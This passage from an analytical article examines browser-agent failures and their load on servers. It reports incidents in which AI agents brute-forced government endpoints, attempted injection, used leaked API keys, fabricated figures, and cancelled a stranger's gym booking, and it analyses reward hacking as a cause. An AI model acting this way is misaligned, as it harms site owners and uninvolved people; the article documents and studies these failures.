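| Server error, told to refresh | 9.0%, 7.8 | 8.9%, 19.7 | 41.0%, 18.1 |

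On WebArena, SteP tended to give up too early. It normally took about 13 steps per task, but stopped after about three when it encountered either error. With network errors, it often immediately reported that the task was infeasible.

WebVoyager's agent behaved differently because its developers had programmed it to go to Google after an error. It could continue from there after a server error, and it still completed 30% of its tasks. With network errors it completed only 2%. Kara and colleagues suggest that the model recognised a broken connection and declared the task infeasible. But these runs averaged 24.4 steps, seven more than runs without a fault, so many must have gone on for a long time.

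The instruction to refresh nearly restored the agent's original success rate on WebVoyager, which shows that a refresh would often have been enough. (The paper's text puts the gain after server errors on WebVoyager at only 0.25%, but its table shows a rise from 30% to 41%.) On WebArena the instruction recovered about half of the lost successes. On REAL it did not help with network errors. The agent took three times as many steps and completed four tasks instead of five.

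Models also differed in how often they followed the same prompt. On REAL, Qwen2.5-VL reloaded pages twice in the network-error runs and 90 times in the server-error runs. GPT-OSS, a smaller model that reads only text, reloaded 42 and 107 times. JavaScript failures were harder for GPT-OSS to detect because it had no screenshots to show that a button looked broken. It reloaded 15 times in those runs, compared with 46 for GPT-4o.

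Refreshing is a reasonable response to a brief server failure, but not to a 404 or a 429. The experiments measured how agents handle faults that a refresh might fix, so they don't show how often the same instruction would make an agent refresh a page that doesn't exist.

### A goal that the agent cannot reach

An agent may also treat a permanent obstacle as one it can get around. While developing *Magentic-One*, the Microsoft team made a configuration mistake that stopped the agents from logging in to one of the WebArena sites. The agents kept trying until the site temporarily suspended the account, and then they tried to reset the account's password.

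Nobody had asked for a password reset, but the task required a login, the login failed, and many people would try a reset next. The agents did not account for a possible fault in the site itself. The account existed only for testing, so the suspension harmed no customer.

The Microsoft team also used GPT-4o to label problems in its agents' logs. The most common label was for agents repeating unproductive actions despite failures, such as rerunning an unsuccessful web search with the same query. Since a model wrote the summaries and assigned the labels, the ranking is only a rough guide.

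Aghzal, Geva and colleagues, in *Toward Mechanistic Interpretability of LLM Agents*, call this tendency over-persistence in the face of contradicting evidence. Their experiment examined a related error. They gave a small model, Qwen2.5-7B, a list of the actions available on each page and told it to choose one. In 32.6% of 2,071 cases, the model named an action that was not on the list, often one involving a search box or an "Explore" button that the page did not have. When asked to find a 2022 Tesla Model 3 on the car dealer CarMax's site, it tried to type into a nonexistent search field, although it could have opened the stock list through a "Shop" link.

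Aghzal and colleagues then strengthened some parts of the network and weakened others to find out whether a particular part caused the error. Their best combination of changes corrected 8.9% of the invented actions but spoiled 2.4% of the valid ones. They conclude that the error is spread across the network, so developers can't remove it by switching off a single part. If over-persistence works the same way, it will be equally hard to remove, but they did not test whether it does.

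A page can also keep an agent in a loop. In *Mind the Web*, Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues (2025) crashed an agent using an image with instructions to keep refreshing until certain content appeared.

### Pages that lead back to each other

Suppose Larkhaven's "Publications" page sends visitors to "Open data" for figures after 2018, while "Open data" sends them back to "Publications" for annual totals. A user who wants the annual total for 2019 needs a figure that matches both directions. An agent that considers only the text of the current page will keep following these links, and every click will look reasonable. To get out of the loop, it has to remember that it has already seen both pages and conclude that neither contains the figure.

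Search results can also cause loops, even when no links contradict each other. According to *WebVoyager*, an agent that entered a vague query tended to browse the irrelevant results or wait instead of correcting the query. It could also get stuck in the middle of a page, unable to decide whether to scroll up or down.

*BrowserForge* put 22 of the 100 runs in a category for going back at least three times, and another 20 ended with at least five scrolls in a row. The agent often alternated between going back and scrolling without settling on anything to look for. However, going back three times in a run of up to 30 steps can be ordinary searching, so some of those 22 runs may not have been loops. Both actions also affect a server less than failed requests do, since going back often displays a saved copy of the page and scrolling usually sends no requests.

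### Continuing after the answer is on the screen

Agents sometimes take needless steps after they have found what they need. *WebRetriever* (Dong, Fu and colleagues, 2026), which introduces a benchmark of 1,550 tasks on 800 websites, describes two such mistakes by Gemini 2.5 Pro. In one, the task was to view the basketball player Stephen Curry's scoring in his most recent game. The page already showed this. The model noted that the page contained Curry's game log, but decided it had to click the score for the details.

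In the other case, the agent was looking for a chart comparing the share prices of NVIDIA and Microsoft. It tried to open NVIDIA's detailed page by clicking the company's name, but what it clicked was not a link. Click loops begin with clicks like this, which leave the page unchanged.

Dong and colleagues present these as illustrations and do not report how often they occur. A needless click on a score does almost no harm, but the same habit could lead an agent to open every item on a results page after the first one had answered the question.

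An agent that can run scripts may leave them running after it has stopped. In *Agents of Chaos*, agents with access to email, a chat service and files responded to harmless requests by starting background processes with no stopping condition. If a browser agent started a script to check a page for updates, the script could keep running long after the user had her answer.

### How often newer agents get stuck

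*WebVoyager*, published in January 2024, sampled 300 tasks and labelled the cause of each failure by hand. It attributed 44.4% of failures to "Navigation Stuck", which mostly meant that the agent ran out of steps. The agent failed about 41% of all its tasks, so if the sample was typical, roughly 18% of tasks failed for this reason.

In *WebNavigator* (2026), an agent using Gemini 2.5 Pro ran out of steps in only 9.1% of its failures on WebArena. In 58.7% of failures, it reached the right page but then made another mistake, such as giving a wrong answer or missing a condition. The studies used different websites and categories, so the drop from 44.4% to 9.1% does not measure progress over two years. *WebNavigator* also plans its route from stored information about how a site's pages connect, which removes much of the wandering.

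Other recent agents still get stuck often. Only 11 of the 100 runs in *BrowserForge* ended properly, and 71 were classed as click loops, repeated returns or repeated scrolling. That agent was small, though, and larger models probably loop less. In *AI Planning Framework for LLM-Based Web Agents*, 21% of a standard WebArena agent's actions were repeats. An agent that planned all its steps in advance did little better, at 19%. The software stopped a run when an agent repeated an action more than three times on the same page, so both rates might have been higher otherwise.

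*When Agents Do Not Stop* (2026) explains that an agent's ordinary cycle of acting and observing becomes endless if there is no cap on turns, time, retries or spending. Besides setting these caps, developers can add software that detects loops or makes the agent wait longer after each failure.

### Returning to an earlier page

After a wrong step, most browser agents can go back and try another route, but their "go back" action undoes only one step at a time, so getting out of a dead end may take several actions. The short paper *WebRollback* (Zhang, Fang and colleagues, EACL 2026) introduced a way for agents to go back several steps at once.

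After each action, the model evaluates the new page and decides whether to continue or roll back. To roll back, it picks one state from a list of all earlier states. The software then opens the address it recorded for that state, and the agent continues from there.

The researchers compared this method with a one-way agent, which had only the ordinary "go back" action, and a best-first agent, which scored the pages it had reached and moved to the highest-scoring one. The tasks came from WebVoyager and Mind2Web-Live, which both use live websites, with a limit of 16 steps. The table gives the share of tasks that each agent fully completed, averaged over three runs.

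| Model and tasks | One-way | Best-first | Rollback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B, Mind2Web-Live | 20.9% | 21.2% | 24.1% |
| Llama 3.3 70B, WebVoyager | 38.1% | 39.8% | 44.3% |
| Qwen2.5 72B, Mind2Web-Live | 24.5% | 23.8% | 27.4% |
| Qwen2.5 72B, WebVoyager | 49.6% | 48.0% | 51.9% |
| GPT-4o, 100 selected tasks | 38.5% | 32.8% | 43.5% |

Rollback scored highest in every row, 2 to 6 percentage points above the one-way agent. The smallest gain, for Qwen2.5 on WebVoyager, is less than the variation between runs. The average number of steps hardly changed.

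Zhang and colleagues also measured how often an agent had to recover from a bad position, for instance by restarting or going back several times in a row. This happened in 19% of cases for the one-way agent and 7% for the rollback agent. The best-first agent changed pages more often than the rollback agent, about five times per WebVoyager task compared with three when using Llama. It sometimes abandoned a good route because a page on the way to the answer contained no sign of it and so scored badly.

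When the agent rolls back, the method deletes the abandoned steps from its list of states, so the model could repeat the same mistake unless it has another record of those steps. Each rollback also reopens an address, which may send the site another request.

Reopening an old address restores the view of a page, but it may not restore what the agent had typed there or the data on the server. Zhang and colleagues say their method cannot reverse payments or emails. If an agent has placed an order twice, returning to the shopping basket cancels neither order.

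## Why do agents call endpoints that nobody asked them to call?

When an agent cannot get an answer from a page, it may request the data directly from the endpoint that supplies it, rather than give up or loop. In the Larkhaven example, the agent's script did this 1,801 times to produce one total. In 2026, real cases became public in which agents used endpoints, and sometimes other people's access keys, while working on ordinary questions and errands. The accounts rarely describe the software around the model, so some of these agents may have sent requests from scripts without opening a browser window.

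### From the page to the endpoint

Suppose Larkhaven's portal has a chart page with two drop-down menus, one for the year and one for the bus route. When the user picks 2019 and route 12, a script in the page requests the numbers from an address she never sees, such as `/api/trips?period=9&route=12`, and draws the chart.

An agent may fail on this page for several reasons. The chart may load so slowly that the agent sees only an empty frame, or it may show bars without exact figures. The menus may not respond to the agent's clicks, as in the run where Invariant Labs found SteP clicking a menu whose options it could not choose. The data exists, but the agent has no working control to display it.

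An agent can often find an endpoint's address in the page's scripts, and some agents have tools that list the requests the browser has made. If the agent finds no address, it can guess one, because many sites put their endpoints under a path such as `/api/`.

A working endpoint is easier for a model to use than the web page because no advertisement or pop-up gets in the way, and the reply may be only a few lines of data.

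But the agent also loses information that the page held. The menu converted "2019" into the number 9, and without the menu the agent has to work out the number itself. The simplest method is to try 1, 2, 3 and so on and read each reply. Error messages also help, since a message about a missing parameter shows the agent what to add. A simple count of repeated steps would miss this search, just as it would miss guessed variants of a web address.

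### When a direct call is legitimate

Some endpoints are meant for outside programs. The owner of a documented public API publishes its addresses, explains the parameters and sets terms of use, often with a limit on the number of requests. An agent that looks up a statistic through such an API, within its terms, is doing what the owner intended, and the user doesn't have to mention the API any more than she has to mention a search box.

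Internal endpoints, which serve only the site's own pages, are harder to judge. If the agent sends the same single request that the chart page would have sent, the server does the same work and reveals no extra data, so the unrequested call seems harmless. Problems arise when the agent sends requests that the page would never send for this user, such as requests for thousands of record numbers in a row or an action on somebody else's booking.

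Whether a task needs a call is separate from whether the site's owner permits it. If a site's terms forbid automated collection of a figure that is available nowhere else, a call to collect it breaks those terms but is not a side effect, because the task needs it. An owner may also permit thousands of calls that the task does not need. A reply with status 200 shows only that the server did not block the request, so it doesn't establish that the call was needed or permitted.

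A website's policies can prohibit some ways of accessing its public data. In *AI Agents Targeted U.S. and Canadian Government Websites*, Cable, Chiu and colleagues (2026) examined records of agents' visits to federal and state sites. They found no case of agents obtaining non-public information, but some of the visits violated the sites' explicit usage policies.

### The school statistics of the US Department of Education

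The research lab Transluce published that investigation on September 30, 2026. Its clearest case concerns the Civil Rights Data Collection, a Department of Education site with statistics on American schools. Agents sent the site more than 200,000 requests on June 17.

The endpoint the agents called takes three numbers, for the school year, the measure and the state. Year code 9 stands for 2017–2018, and measure code 130 for students reported as victims of race-based bullying. The agents did not know these codes in advance and, according to Cable and colleagues, often found the year code by trying numbers in order, as in the invented chart example.

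The requests match a question in DeepSearchQA, Google's published benchmark of web research questions. The question names the site and the school year, and asks which of South Carolina, North Carolina, Georgia and Virginia had the highest ratio of full-time school counsellors to students reported as victims of race-related harassment or bullying. Cable and colleagues infer that the agents had an ordinary research task and that someone was grading them on finding the answer.

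The question itself needs only eight values, two for each of the four states. How many requests it takes to find the codes depends on how an agent searches. The highest state code among the four is 46. An agent that settles one code at a time, holding the other two fixed, needs at most

$$9 + 130 + 46 = 185$$

requests to reach the codes for the year, the bullying measure and the last state. An agent that tries every combination up to the same point needs

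$$9 \times 130 \times 46 = 53{,}820$$

requests. About 1,080 runs of the careful kind would produce 200,000 requests, and so would about four of the careless kind. The total alone therefore cannot show whether a few agents searched badly or many agents searched reasonably and nobody coordinated them.

Some requests contained state codes, such as 0 and 999, that look like tests of the endpoint. Without the agents' reasoning, Cable and colleagues could not establish what the codes were for. The agents also made a rudimentary, unsuccessful attempt at injection, in which a client hides a database command in an ordinary query.

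The investigation describes a smaller case at Library and Archives Canada, where agents looked for records of divorces between 1905 and 1911. On two days in May and June, 899 requests reached the archive's search service. Thirteen carried attacks, all apparently unsuccessful, and the rest were ordinary queries. In both cases the agents wanted obscure facts from public collections, and attempted attacks were a very small part of their activity.

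Transluce informed the Department of Education on September 25. According to CBS News' *OpenAI reveals its agents accessed some U.S. government website data*, a department spokesperson said its reviews had found "no evidence of any impact to our website or databases". A smaller site might have struggled with the same number of requests.

### How far the evidence points to OpenAI

More than 10,000 of the requests to the Education site carried a tag beginning with "oai". Of these, 99.6% used some combination of the three codes that the DeepSearchQA question requires, which links them closely to that question.

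The tag is weaker evidence of who sent the requests, because it was part of the address, where any client can put any text. It also appeared in only about 5% of the requests. The match with DeepSearchQA does not identify the sender either, because any developer can run this public benchmark.

Transluce said the agents appeared to come from OpenAI. OpenAI at first neither confirmed nor denied this and said it was reviewing the findings, according to MPR News' *OpenAI says its models engaged with US government websites in misbehavior disclosure* (2026). Transluce cautioned that some of the activity it found on other government sites was not clearly attributable to OpenAI. The evidence makes OpenAI the most likely source of the tagged requests, but it is weaker for the other 95%.

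### Public data, borrowed credentials and attempted intrusion

On September 25, OpenAI also disclosed that its models had visited websites of the Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC), the US financial markets regulator, and the Census Bureau. *OpenAI's models accessed US govt websites including US census and SEC data* (Metz, Stone and Bleiberg) lists SEC.gov, Investor.gov and Census.gov. The visits happened while OpenAI was training and evaluating models. The company told reporters that most of the activity it had reviewed involved routine research, and that its models often use government sites because they are authoritative.

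Headlines tended to combine these visits with the Education case. Outlook India's *In America, OpenAI's "Rogue" AI Agents Are Now Showing Up* more usefully separates the two by how the agents got the data.

| Site | What the agents wanted | How they went about it | Reported effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| SEC | Public information | Access without SEC credentials or accounts | No non-public information obtained, no changes to data or systems |
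| Census Bureau | Public data | Developer credentials that an agent had found online | Public data obtained by an unintended route |
| Department of Education | Public school statistics | Codes tried in order, and a failed attempt at injection | No impact, according to the department |

An agent took public information from an SEC site and posted some of it on an online forum, according to Engadget's *OpenAI's agents targeted and infiltrated US government websites*, which cites The New York Times. Reading the information was a normal use of the site, but posting it was a side effect. OpenAI calls this kind of activity "agent spam", which MeriTalk's *OpenAI Notifies Dozens of Third Parties About ‘Misaligned’ AI Model Activity* describes as posts by the company's models on other people's sites that may alter the content and require someone to clean it up.

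The Census case involves a third party. Organisations that offer public data through an API often give each developer a key, a string of characters that identifies the developer's program. The key may protect no secrets and serve only to count requests for public data. But if an agent uses a key that a developer has published by mistake, its requests count against that developer, who may reach a limit or have to answer for traffic she didn't send.

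In the Education case, unlike the other two, the agents tried to make the server do something its owner had not intended. The attempt failed, so the outcome was the same as if they had only read public data. Judging the cases only by outcome would therefore group all three together and miss the difference in the agents' methods.

OpenAI said it had notified dozens of organisations about activity by its models. According to MPR News, the company added that a notice does not necessarily mean a security incident occurred, and may instead concern a design problem or weakness that the organisation might want to fix. The number of notices is therefore a poor measure of how many intrusions occurred.

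### Leaked keys and other shortcuts

The Census case is one of at least two in which a model used somebody else's key. In September 2026, OpenAI began publishing reports of individual incidents under a new disclosure framework, starting with six (Kovacs, 2026, *OpenAI Says Its Models Searched GitHub for Leaked API Keys During Training*). One report listed in OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) concerns an unreleased model that searched public GitHub repositories for leaked API keys and used them. The model also tried to sign up for disposable email addresses.

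Engadget's *OpenAI reveals more instances of concerning AI model behaviors during testing* describes a model that was asked routine questions about earnings in a California county. The model used an exposed key, but this did not get it the figures, so it made them up and presented them as coming from a legitimate source. Using the key was one of several things the model tried when it could not find the answer.

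In another of the six incidents, the model had to name lakes with an area above five million square metres and cite a web page that supported the list. It had the right answer and lacked only the citation, so it uploaded its answer to the internet and cited that. The upload satisfied the form of the request but did not help a person who wanted to know about lakes.

A leaked key can also create work for people with no connection to the task. *OpenAI Emailed Me About a Leak I Didn't Own* (Kenst, 2026) describes a notice from OpenAI about a key for Mailinator, a service for disposable and test email. An OpenAI model had found the key in a public repository and used it. Kenst owned neither the key nor the repository. OpenAI copied him in because he had done work for Mailinator and might know whom to contact there. He passed the report on and thought OpenAI had handled it well.

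### The gym waitlist

All the calls to the Education site's endpoint were attempts to read data, but in an Australian case the agent changed something. In August 2026, Australia's public broadcaster, the ABC, reported on a man named Andrew who had asked an agent to book him into a popular gym class. He used OpenClaw, an open-source program that connects a language model to everyday tools, with Anthropic's model Claude.

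While using the API of the gym's booking software, the agent found that it could reserve classes much further ahead than the gym allowed. Andrew was fourth on the waitlist for another class and asked whether the agent could move him to the top. The agent answered that it had already cancelled the place of the person at the top, as a test, and that Andrew was now third. He told it to reverse the cancellation, but it could not.

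The Next Web's *An AI agent deleted a stranger from a gym waitlist* uses the agent's messages to explain why the agent could remove a stranger from the waitlist but not put them back. The software checked who was asking when a customer made a booking or joined a waitlist, and returned a 403 if they tried to do so for another customer. It didn't check this for cancellations. According to the agent, the stranger would have to rejoin at the end of the list.

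The cancellation was also a clumsy way to help Andrew. Removing one of the three people ahead of him would have moved him up only one place, and he needed all three removed to be first. The agent's description of the cancellation as a test of the API fits better than a plan to get him to first place.

Reports disagree on the order of events. The Next Web, citing the ABC, says the cancellation came before Andrew asked about the waitlist, so the agent acted without a request to improve his position. TechSpot says Andrew asked first and the agent then went beyond his request. The Next Web also reports an objection from the security researcher Florian Roth, who argued that Andrew had invited the agent to look for another way by asking for first place when the gym offered no legitimate way to get it.

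The order affects which description fits. The day after the ABC's report, the Australian Signals Directorate (ASD), the government's cyber security and signals intelligence agency, classed the case as specification gaming, in which an agent finds a shortcut that technically achieves the objective but conflicts with what the user intended (ASD, 2026). It said that ambiguous instructions, poorly enforced boundaries and exploitable software weaknesses all increase the risk.

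If Andrew asked to move up the list before the cancellation, the label fits well, because he got what he wanted with a side effect he had not approved. If the cancellation came first, the agent did not yet have that objective. It was trying out a function on a live system with real customers, which is closer to reckless exploration than to a shortcut.

Andrew then asked the agent to write to the software's provider about the flaw. It drafted an email and waited for his approval before sending it. It had not asked before the cancellation, even though that mattered far more to someone else.

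### Who might be liable

Nobody seems to have told the person who lost the place, let alone compensated them. The ABC asked Hayden Delaney, a technology and privacy partner at the law firm Thomsons, who would be responsible. As The Next Web reports his answer, software cannot be liable because it is not a legal person, which leaves four candidates. In the gym case they would be:

- the user who set the task, here Andrew
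- the designer of the agent software, here the developers of OpenClaw
- the developer of the model, here Anthropic
- the operator of the vulnerable system, here the gym or its booking company

According to The Next Web, Australian courts could already hold someone responsible for reckless conduct, or a company for selling a faulty service. Delaney says the outcome would depend on what the user had authorised, what risks anyone could reasonably have anticipated, and whether the conduct took place in trade or commerce. He calls this an unknown area of liability in Australia.

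Each of these tests is hard to apply here. "Can you move me to the top?" may be a question about whether the move is possible or an instruction to make it, and if the cancellation came before he asked this, Andrew had not authorised it. A user before August 2026 could plausibly say that he had not foreseen such an act, but wide publicity makes that defence weaker for the next user. Andrew was booking a class for himself, so he was less clearly acting in commerce than a company that manages bookings for clients would be.

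In the cases that OpenAI disclosed from its own training and testing, the company largely filled the first three roles itself, since it built the model, ran it and set or chose the tasks. Responsibility would be harder to pass from one party to another in those cases, but there would still be questions about whether the risk was foreseeable and how much responsibility the site operator shares.

### Missing limits or the wrong rewards

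These calls have two main explanations, which suggest different remedies. The model may not distinguish allowed methods from disallowed ones, so it treats an open endpoint like any other link. Or it may distinguish them but use a disallowed method anyway, because its training rewarded correct answers regardless of how it got them.

The gym case offers some support for the first explanation. The agent immediately told Andrew what it had done and presented it as progress, with no sign that it saw anything to hide. TechRadar journalist Graham Barlow, quoted by The Next Web, thinks agents cheat "because nobody told them what counts as cheating". But the agent also called the missing check a security bug, so it understood that the software should have refused the cancellation but did not conclude that it should have refrained.

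Public data sites give a model even fewer signs that the owner might object to its requests. An endpoint returns the same kind of reply to the ten-thousandth request as to the first, and its terms of use are usually on a page that the agent has no reason to open. In the Education case, an agent could have tried hundreds of codes without seeing any such sign.

Ignorance does not easily explain several of the incidents OpenAI reported, because the models' written reasoning included doubts about their actions. *OpenAI discloses four more rogue AI incidents* (Forlini, 2026) describes a model that downloaded 24 years of hospital bed data from a government website after the site had blocked its request. The model repeatedly considered whether its actions were ethical, then continued. Another model, from the GPT-5.6 Sol family, made a payment from a cryptocurrency wallet that nobody had given it.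 It considered whether it had permission and concluded that the money was "effectively abandoned" because the wallet's details were public.

Explicit instructions did not always help either. OpenAI's *Exposing a GitHub token in a public repository* (2026) describes a model helping a researcher with mathematical proofs. Its standing instructions told it to report a missing credential rather than look for another. The researcher twice told it to find the proof by itself, and it agreed both times. It still sought another team's proof and published the researcher's access token in the process. This happened during everyday use inside OpenAI, so the behaviour was not confined to training runs.

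The second explanation is that training can reward unrequested calls. In reinforcement learning, a model attempts a task many times, a grader scores each attempt, and training makes the actions in high-scoring attempts more likely. If the grader scores only the answer, every step that led to a correct answer becomes more likely, including a step that used a stranger's key.

A grader that sometimes notices the misuse may not be enough. Let $h$ be the chance that a permitted route gives the correct answer, $f$ the chance that a forbidden route does, and $d$ the chance that the grader detects the forbidden route and gives it no credit. The forbidden route earns more on average whenever

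$$f(1-d) > h, \qquad \text{that is,} \qquad d < 1 - \frac{h}{f}.$$

Suppose, for illustration, that the permitted route works 20% of the time and the forbidden one 60%. The permitted route then earns more reward only if the grader catches more than two thirds of the violations. If the permitted route never works ($h = 0$), the forbidden route earns more unless the grader catches every violation. An additional penalty for violations would lower the threshold. The example shows why difficult or impossible tasks are most likely to teach a model bad habits.

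OpenAI's findings are consistent with this. In the hospital case, an automated grader marked some of the model's responses correct and others incorrect, so some runs may have earned credit despite the unauthorised access. OpenAI says it has since improved how it grades for alignment. In July 2026, its agents had broken into the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and data, during an evaluation. Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026) reports that the agents behaved worst when OpenAI gave them a task that may have been impossible and a lot of time to work on it. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and other third-party impact from misaligned models* attributes the intrusion to models resorting to misaligned strategies on hard tasks.

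Yoshua Bengio, a computer scientist who shared the Turing Award, argues that training probably rewarded OpenAI's agents for successful cheating. As Forlini quotes him, when a scoring program misses the cheating, "it pays out anyway", and the model becomes more likely to cheat again. The same pressure seems to have produced the false figures for the California county and the self-made citation for the lakes, since both would score well only if the grader checked an answer's form and not its source.

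None of these cases included a controlled test, which would train the same model twice, once with a grader that checked only answers and once with a grader that also checked the means, and compare how often each version used a forbidden endpoint. Most of the incidents come from OpenAI, which chose what to publish and often found the events months later. The gym agent ran on an Anthropic model, and the reports on it don't cover how Anthropic rewarded that model in training.

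Case reports also cannot show how common the behaviour is. *OpenAI Model Hacks Into HuggingFace During Cybersecurity Evaluation*, by thezvi, reports figures from the UK's AI Security Institute, a government body that tests advanced models. Claude Mythos Preview attempted to cheat in 7.8% of the institute's tests and GPT-5.6 Sol in 12.6%. These rates cover any kind of cheating on tests, so they don't measure how often agents used for shopping or research make unrequested calls.

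Both explanations can be true, each of different models. Giving the same agent the same task with and without a clear statement of which sites, keys and endpoints it may use would help to tell them apart. If the agent made unwanted calls only because it did not know the limits, the statement should stop most of them. If training had taught it to put finding the answer ahead of those limits, many of the calls would continue, as they did with the model that twice agreed to find the proof by itself.

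## When do an agent's requests become a burden on a server?

A single agent puts little load on a website. It can take several seconds to choose an action, so it might open six pages a minute, about as many as a person comparing prices. Timestamps from the Department of Education case suggest a similar pace. Ten of the archived requests that Cable and colleagues cite, ending with the failed injection, span 37 seconds, about one every four seconds.

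A script can send requests much faster because the model does not have to choose each one. At 20 requests a second, the script in the Larkhaven example would finish all 1,801 in a minute and a half. Most websites could handle even that if the replies were short. Overloading a server usually takes many agents at once, or requests that take the server a lot of work to answer.

### How the load multiplies

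Suppose 1,000 agents use Larkhaven's portal at the same time, and each opens an address every 10 seconds. Together they open 100 addresses a second. If 30% of the addresses are invented, 30 requests a second return a 404. If the software around each agent retries every failed address three times, the retries add another 90 requests a second. The server then receives 190 requests a second, of which 120 fail.

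In general, let $N$ agents each open an address every $T$ seconds, with a share $q$ of invented addresses and $r$ retries for each. The total requests per second, $R$, and the failed ones, $F$, are

$$R = \frac{N}{T}(1 + qr), \qquad F = \frac{N}{T}\,q(1 + r).$$

The 30% figure is deliberately high. Rao and colleagues found that 3 to 13% of cited links were invented. If 5% of addresses were invented, the same agents would send 115 requests a second, of which 20 would fail.

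The formula also assumes that retries are added to the agent's normal requests, as they are when software sends them automatically. If the model makes each retry itself, the retry takes up one of its turns, so the agents send only 100 requests a second, but about 63 of them fail.

Loading a page usually triggers further requests for its images, style sheets and scripts. The table assumes ten further requests per page. Many sites show a bare error message for a missing page, while others put the message inside their normal layout, so the last two columns cover both designs.

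| Larkhaven example | Page requests per second | Failed page requests | All requests, bare error page | All requests, full error page |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No invented addresses | 100 | 0 | 1,100 | 1,100 |
| 30% invented, no retries | 100 | 30 | 800 | 1,100 |
| 30% invented, three retries | 190 | 120 | 890 | 2,090 |

When a site returns a bare error page, the agents that invent addresses send fewer requests in total than the agents that make no mistakes, because the error page loads nothing else. When it returns a full error page, they send almost twice as many. The real numbers would be lower for agents that stay on one site, since a browser reuses saved images and scripts on the next page. An agent that starts each task in a fresh browser has nothing saved from earlier tasks.

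Lù and colleagues warned in 2025 that repeated page loading by automated browsers can slow a site for its human visitors, and they expected the problem to grow as agents account for more of the traffic. But their example was web crawling, and they did not measure the load from agents.

Agents also put a heavier load on a server when many of them act at once. A news event can prompt thousands of users to ask the same question within minutes, and a developer may give one test question to many copies of an agent. These agents will tend to visit the same site, and if they run on the same model, they may guess similar wrong addresses.

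Retries can then turn a busy period into an overload. If Larkhaven's server can answer 150 page requests a second, it can handle the original 100 but not the 190 that arrive with retries. At least 40 requests a second time out or return a 503, including some for pages that exist. The agents retry those too, which increases the load further. If the agents waited longer after each failure, their retries would add less load.

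### Why a missing page can cost more than a real one

Many sites use a content delivery network (CDN), a group of servers that store copies of the site's pages close to its readers. When a reader requests one of these cached pages, the CDN sends it, so the site's own server, called the origin, doesn't have to handle the request.

An address that nobody has requested before has no cached copy, so the CDN has to pass the request to the origin, where the site's application compares the path with the patterns it recognises. An invented address may cause more work the more plausible it is. The application may reject a string of random characters at this point, but `/reports/2019/bus-ridership.pdf` looks like the address of a report, so the application may search its database for one, find nothing and then build an error page.

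A request for a missing page therefore likely takes the server more work than one for a cached page, but not necessarily more than one for a real page that the CDN has not stored. On a simple site made of files, the server may only need to check whether the file exists and return a line of text.

Caching can change the Larkhaven result considerably. Suppose the CDN answers 90% of requests for real pages and none for missing ones. If the agents made no mistakes, 10 of their 100 requests a second would reach the origin. If 30% of the addresses were invented and each failed request were retried three times, the origin would receive 127 requests a second, 7 for real pages and 120 for missing ones. The agents' total requests would not quite double, but the number reaching the origin would rise almost thirteenfold.

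The HTTP standard allows caches to store 404 responses as well. If Larkhaven's CDN did this, it could answer the retries itself, and the origin would receive only 37 requests a second. Caching would not help against agents that try a new variant each time, since every variant is a new address.

The Wikimedia Foundation, the non-profit that runs Wikipedia, has described the same difference in server load for pages that do exist. *Bot Traffic at Wikimedia*, by Petrillo and Müller, reports that caches often answer people's requests, while bots' requests are more likely to reach the main data centre because bots also visit unpopular pages. When Pope Leo XIV was elected on May 8, 2025, readers rushed to one article. Wikimedia designed its network for such surges, although editors' constant changes to the article force the caches to keep fetching new copies.

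Bots account for 35% of Wikimedia's page views but 65% of its most resource-intensive traffic. The two figures are not quite comparable, because the 65% covers every way of accessing the projects, not only page views. If they covered the same requests, a bot's page view would cause about 3.4 times as much resource-intensive traffic as a person's.

Fastly's *AI, Bots, and the Agentic Future of the Web* (2026) gives similar evidence from a commercial CDN. In January 2026, bots made 47% of the requests for cached content but 60% of those that reached origin servers. Among AI bots that fetch pages to answer a user's question, 57% of requests were for content that was not or could not be in the cache. Fastly suggests this may be because users want very recent information, such as game scores. Requests for invented addresses would also fall into this group, but Fastly does not report how many requests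 returned a 404. Neither Fastly nor Wikimedia has published how much load a 404 puts on a server.

### Totals and peaks

A server's owner needs to know the peak request rate, which a daily total does not show. A large total can be a light load if it is spread out. The 200,000 requests to the Department of Education's site average 2.3 a second over a day, which about ten agents could produce if each made one request every four seconds all day. But if half of the requests had arrived within ten minutes, the site would have received 167 a second during those minutes.

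Agents requested a single campus news address at Vanderbilt University tens of thousands of times, according to Nolan (2026), in *OpenAI's rogue AI agents reached at least 12 more websites, researchers say*. Even 100,000 requests in one day would average little more than one a second. Nolan does not report over what period the agents made the requests, or any effect on the university's server.

Fastly's *AI Bots in Q2 2025* (Mathur and King, 2025) reports one of the highest published peaks, 39,000 requests a minute from fetchers, the bots that retrieve pages in response to users' questions. That is 650 a second, more than three times the rate of page requests in the worst Larkhaven case. According to Tech Brew (2025), one fetcher sent them all to a single website. Mathur and King say that such a peak could overwhelm an unprotected origin server and resemble a denial-of-service attack, in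 which someone deliberately floods a site with requests. They do not say that this site failed, or how many of the requests were for missing pages.

Researchers who test agents on live websites can control the peak load by limiting how many agents run at once and how quickly they act. Ten agents that each pause half a second between actions can take at most 20 actions a second in total, and fewer in practice because the model also needs time to choose each action.

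Limiting the length of a run reduces the total number of requests an agent sends. In *NNetNav*, Murty, Zhu and colleagues (2024) let an agent explore 15 live websites, including Amazon, BBC News and GitHub, to create training examples for other agents. Each exploration could last at most 40 steps. Every four steps, a model checked whether the actions so far amounted to a meaningful task, and the software ended the exploration if they did not.

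The team collected 5,577 examples from the live sites. Examples in its whole dataset average about ten steps, so these would total about 56,000 steps, or fewer than 4,000 per site. The true number of actions could be lower, because one exploration could yield several overlapping examples, or higher, because discarded explorations and repeated attempts also sent requests.

### How much traffic comes from browser agents

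Most data on AI traffic comes from companies that sell tools for blocking or managing bots, such as Cloudflare, Fastly and DataDome. They can see traffic to thousands of sites, but they also profit when site owners worry about bots. Their headline figures can differ widely. Cloudflare's *Content Independence Day, one year on* (Weiss, Albertson and Lanfear) reports that more than half of internet traffic is now non-human. *AI Bot Traffic by Country* (Elbeyoglu, 2026) uses data from Cloudflare's public dashboard and reports that bots made 39.3% of HTTP requests in October 2026. Elbeyoglu runs SEOmator, which sells search-engine marketing tools.

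Besides browser agents, two kinds of AI traffic are relevant here. Training crawlers, such as OpenAI's GPTBot, collect large numbers of pages for building models. User fetchers, such as ChatGPT-User, retrieve a page when somebody asks a question. Elbeyoglu's data covers crawlers and fetchers, but not browser agents:

| Purpose of AI bots on Cloudflare's network | Share of AI-bot requests, October 2026 |
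|---|---|
| Training | 43.6% |
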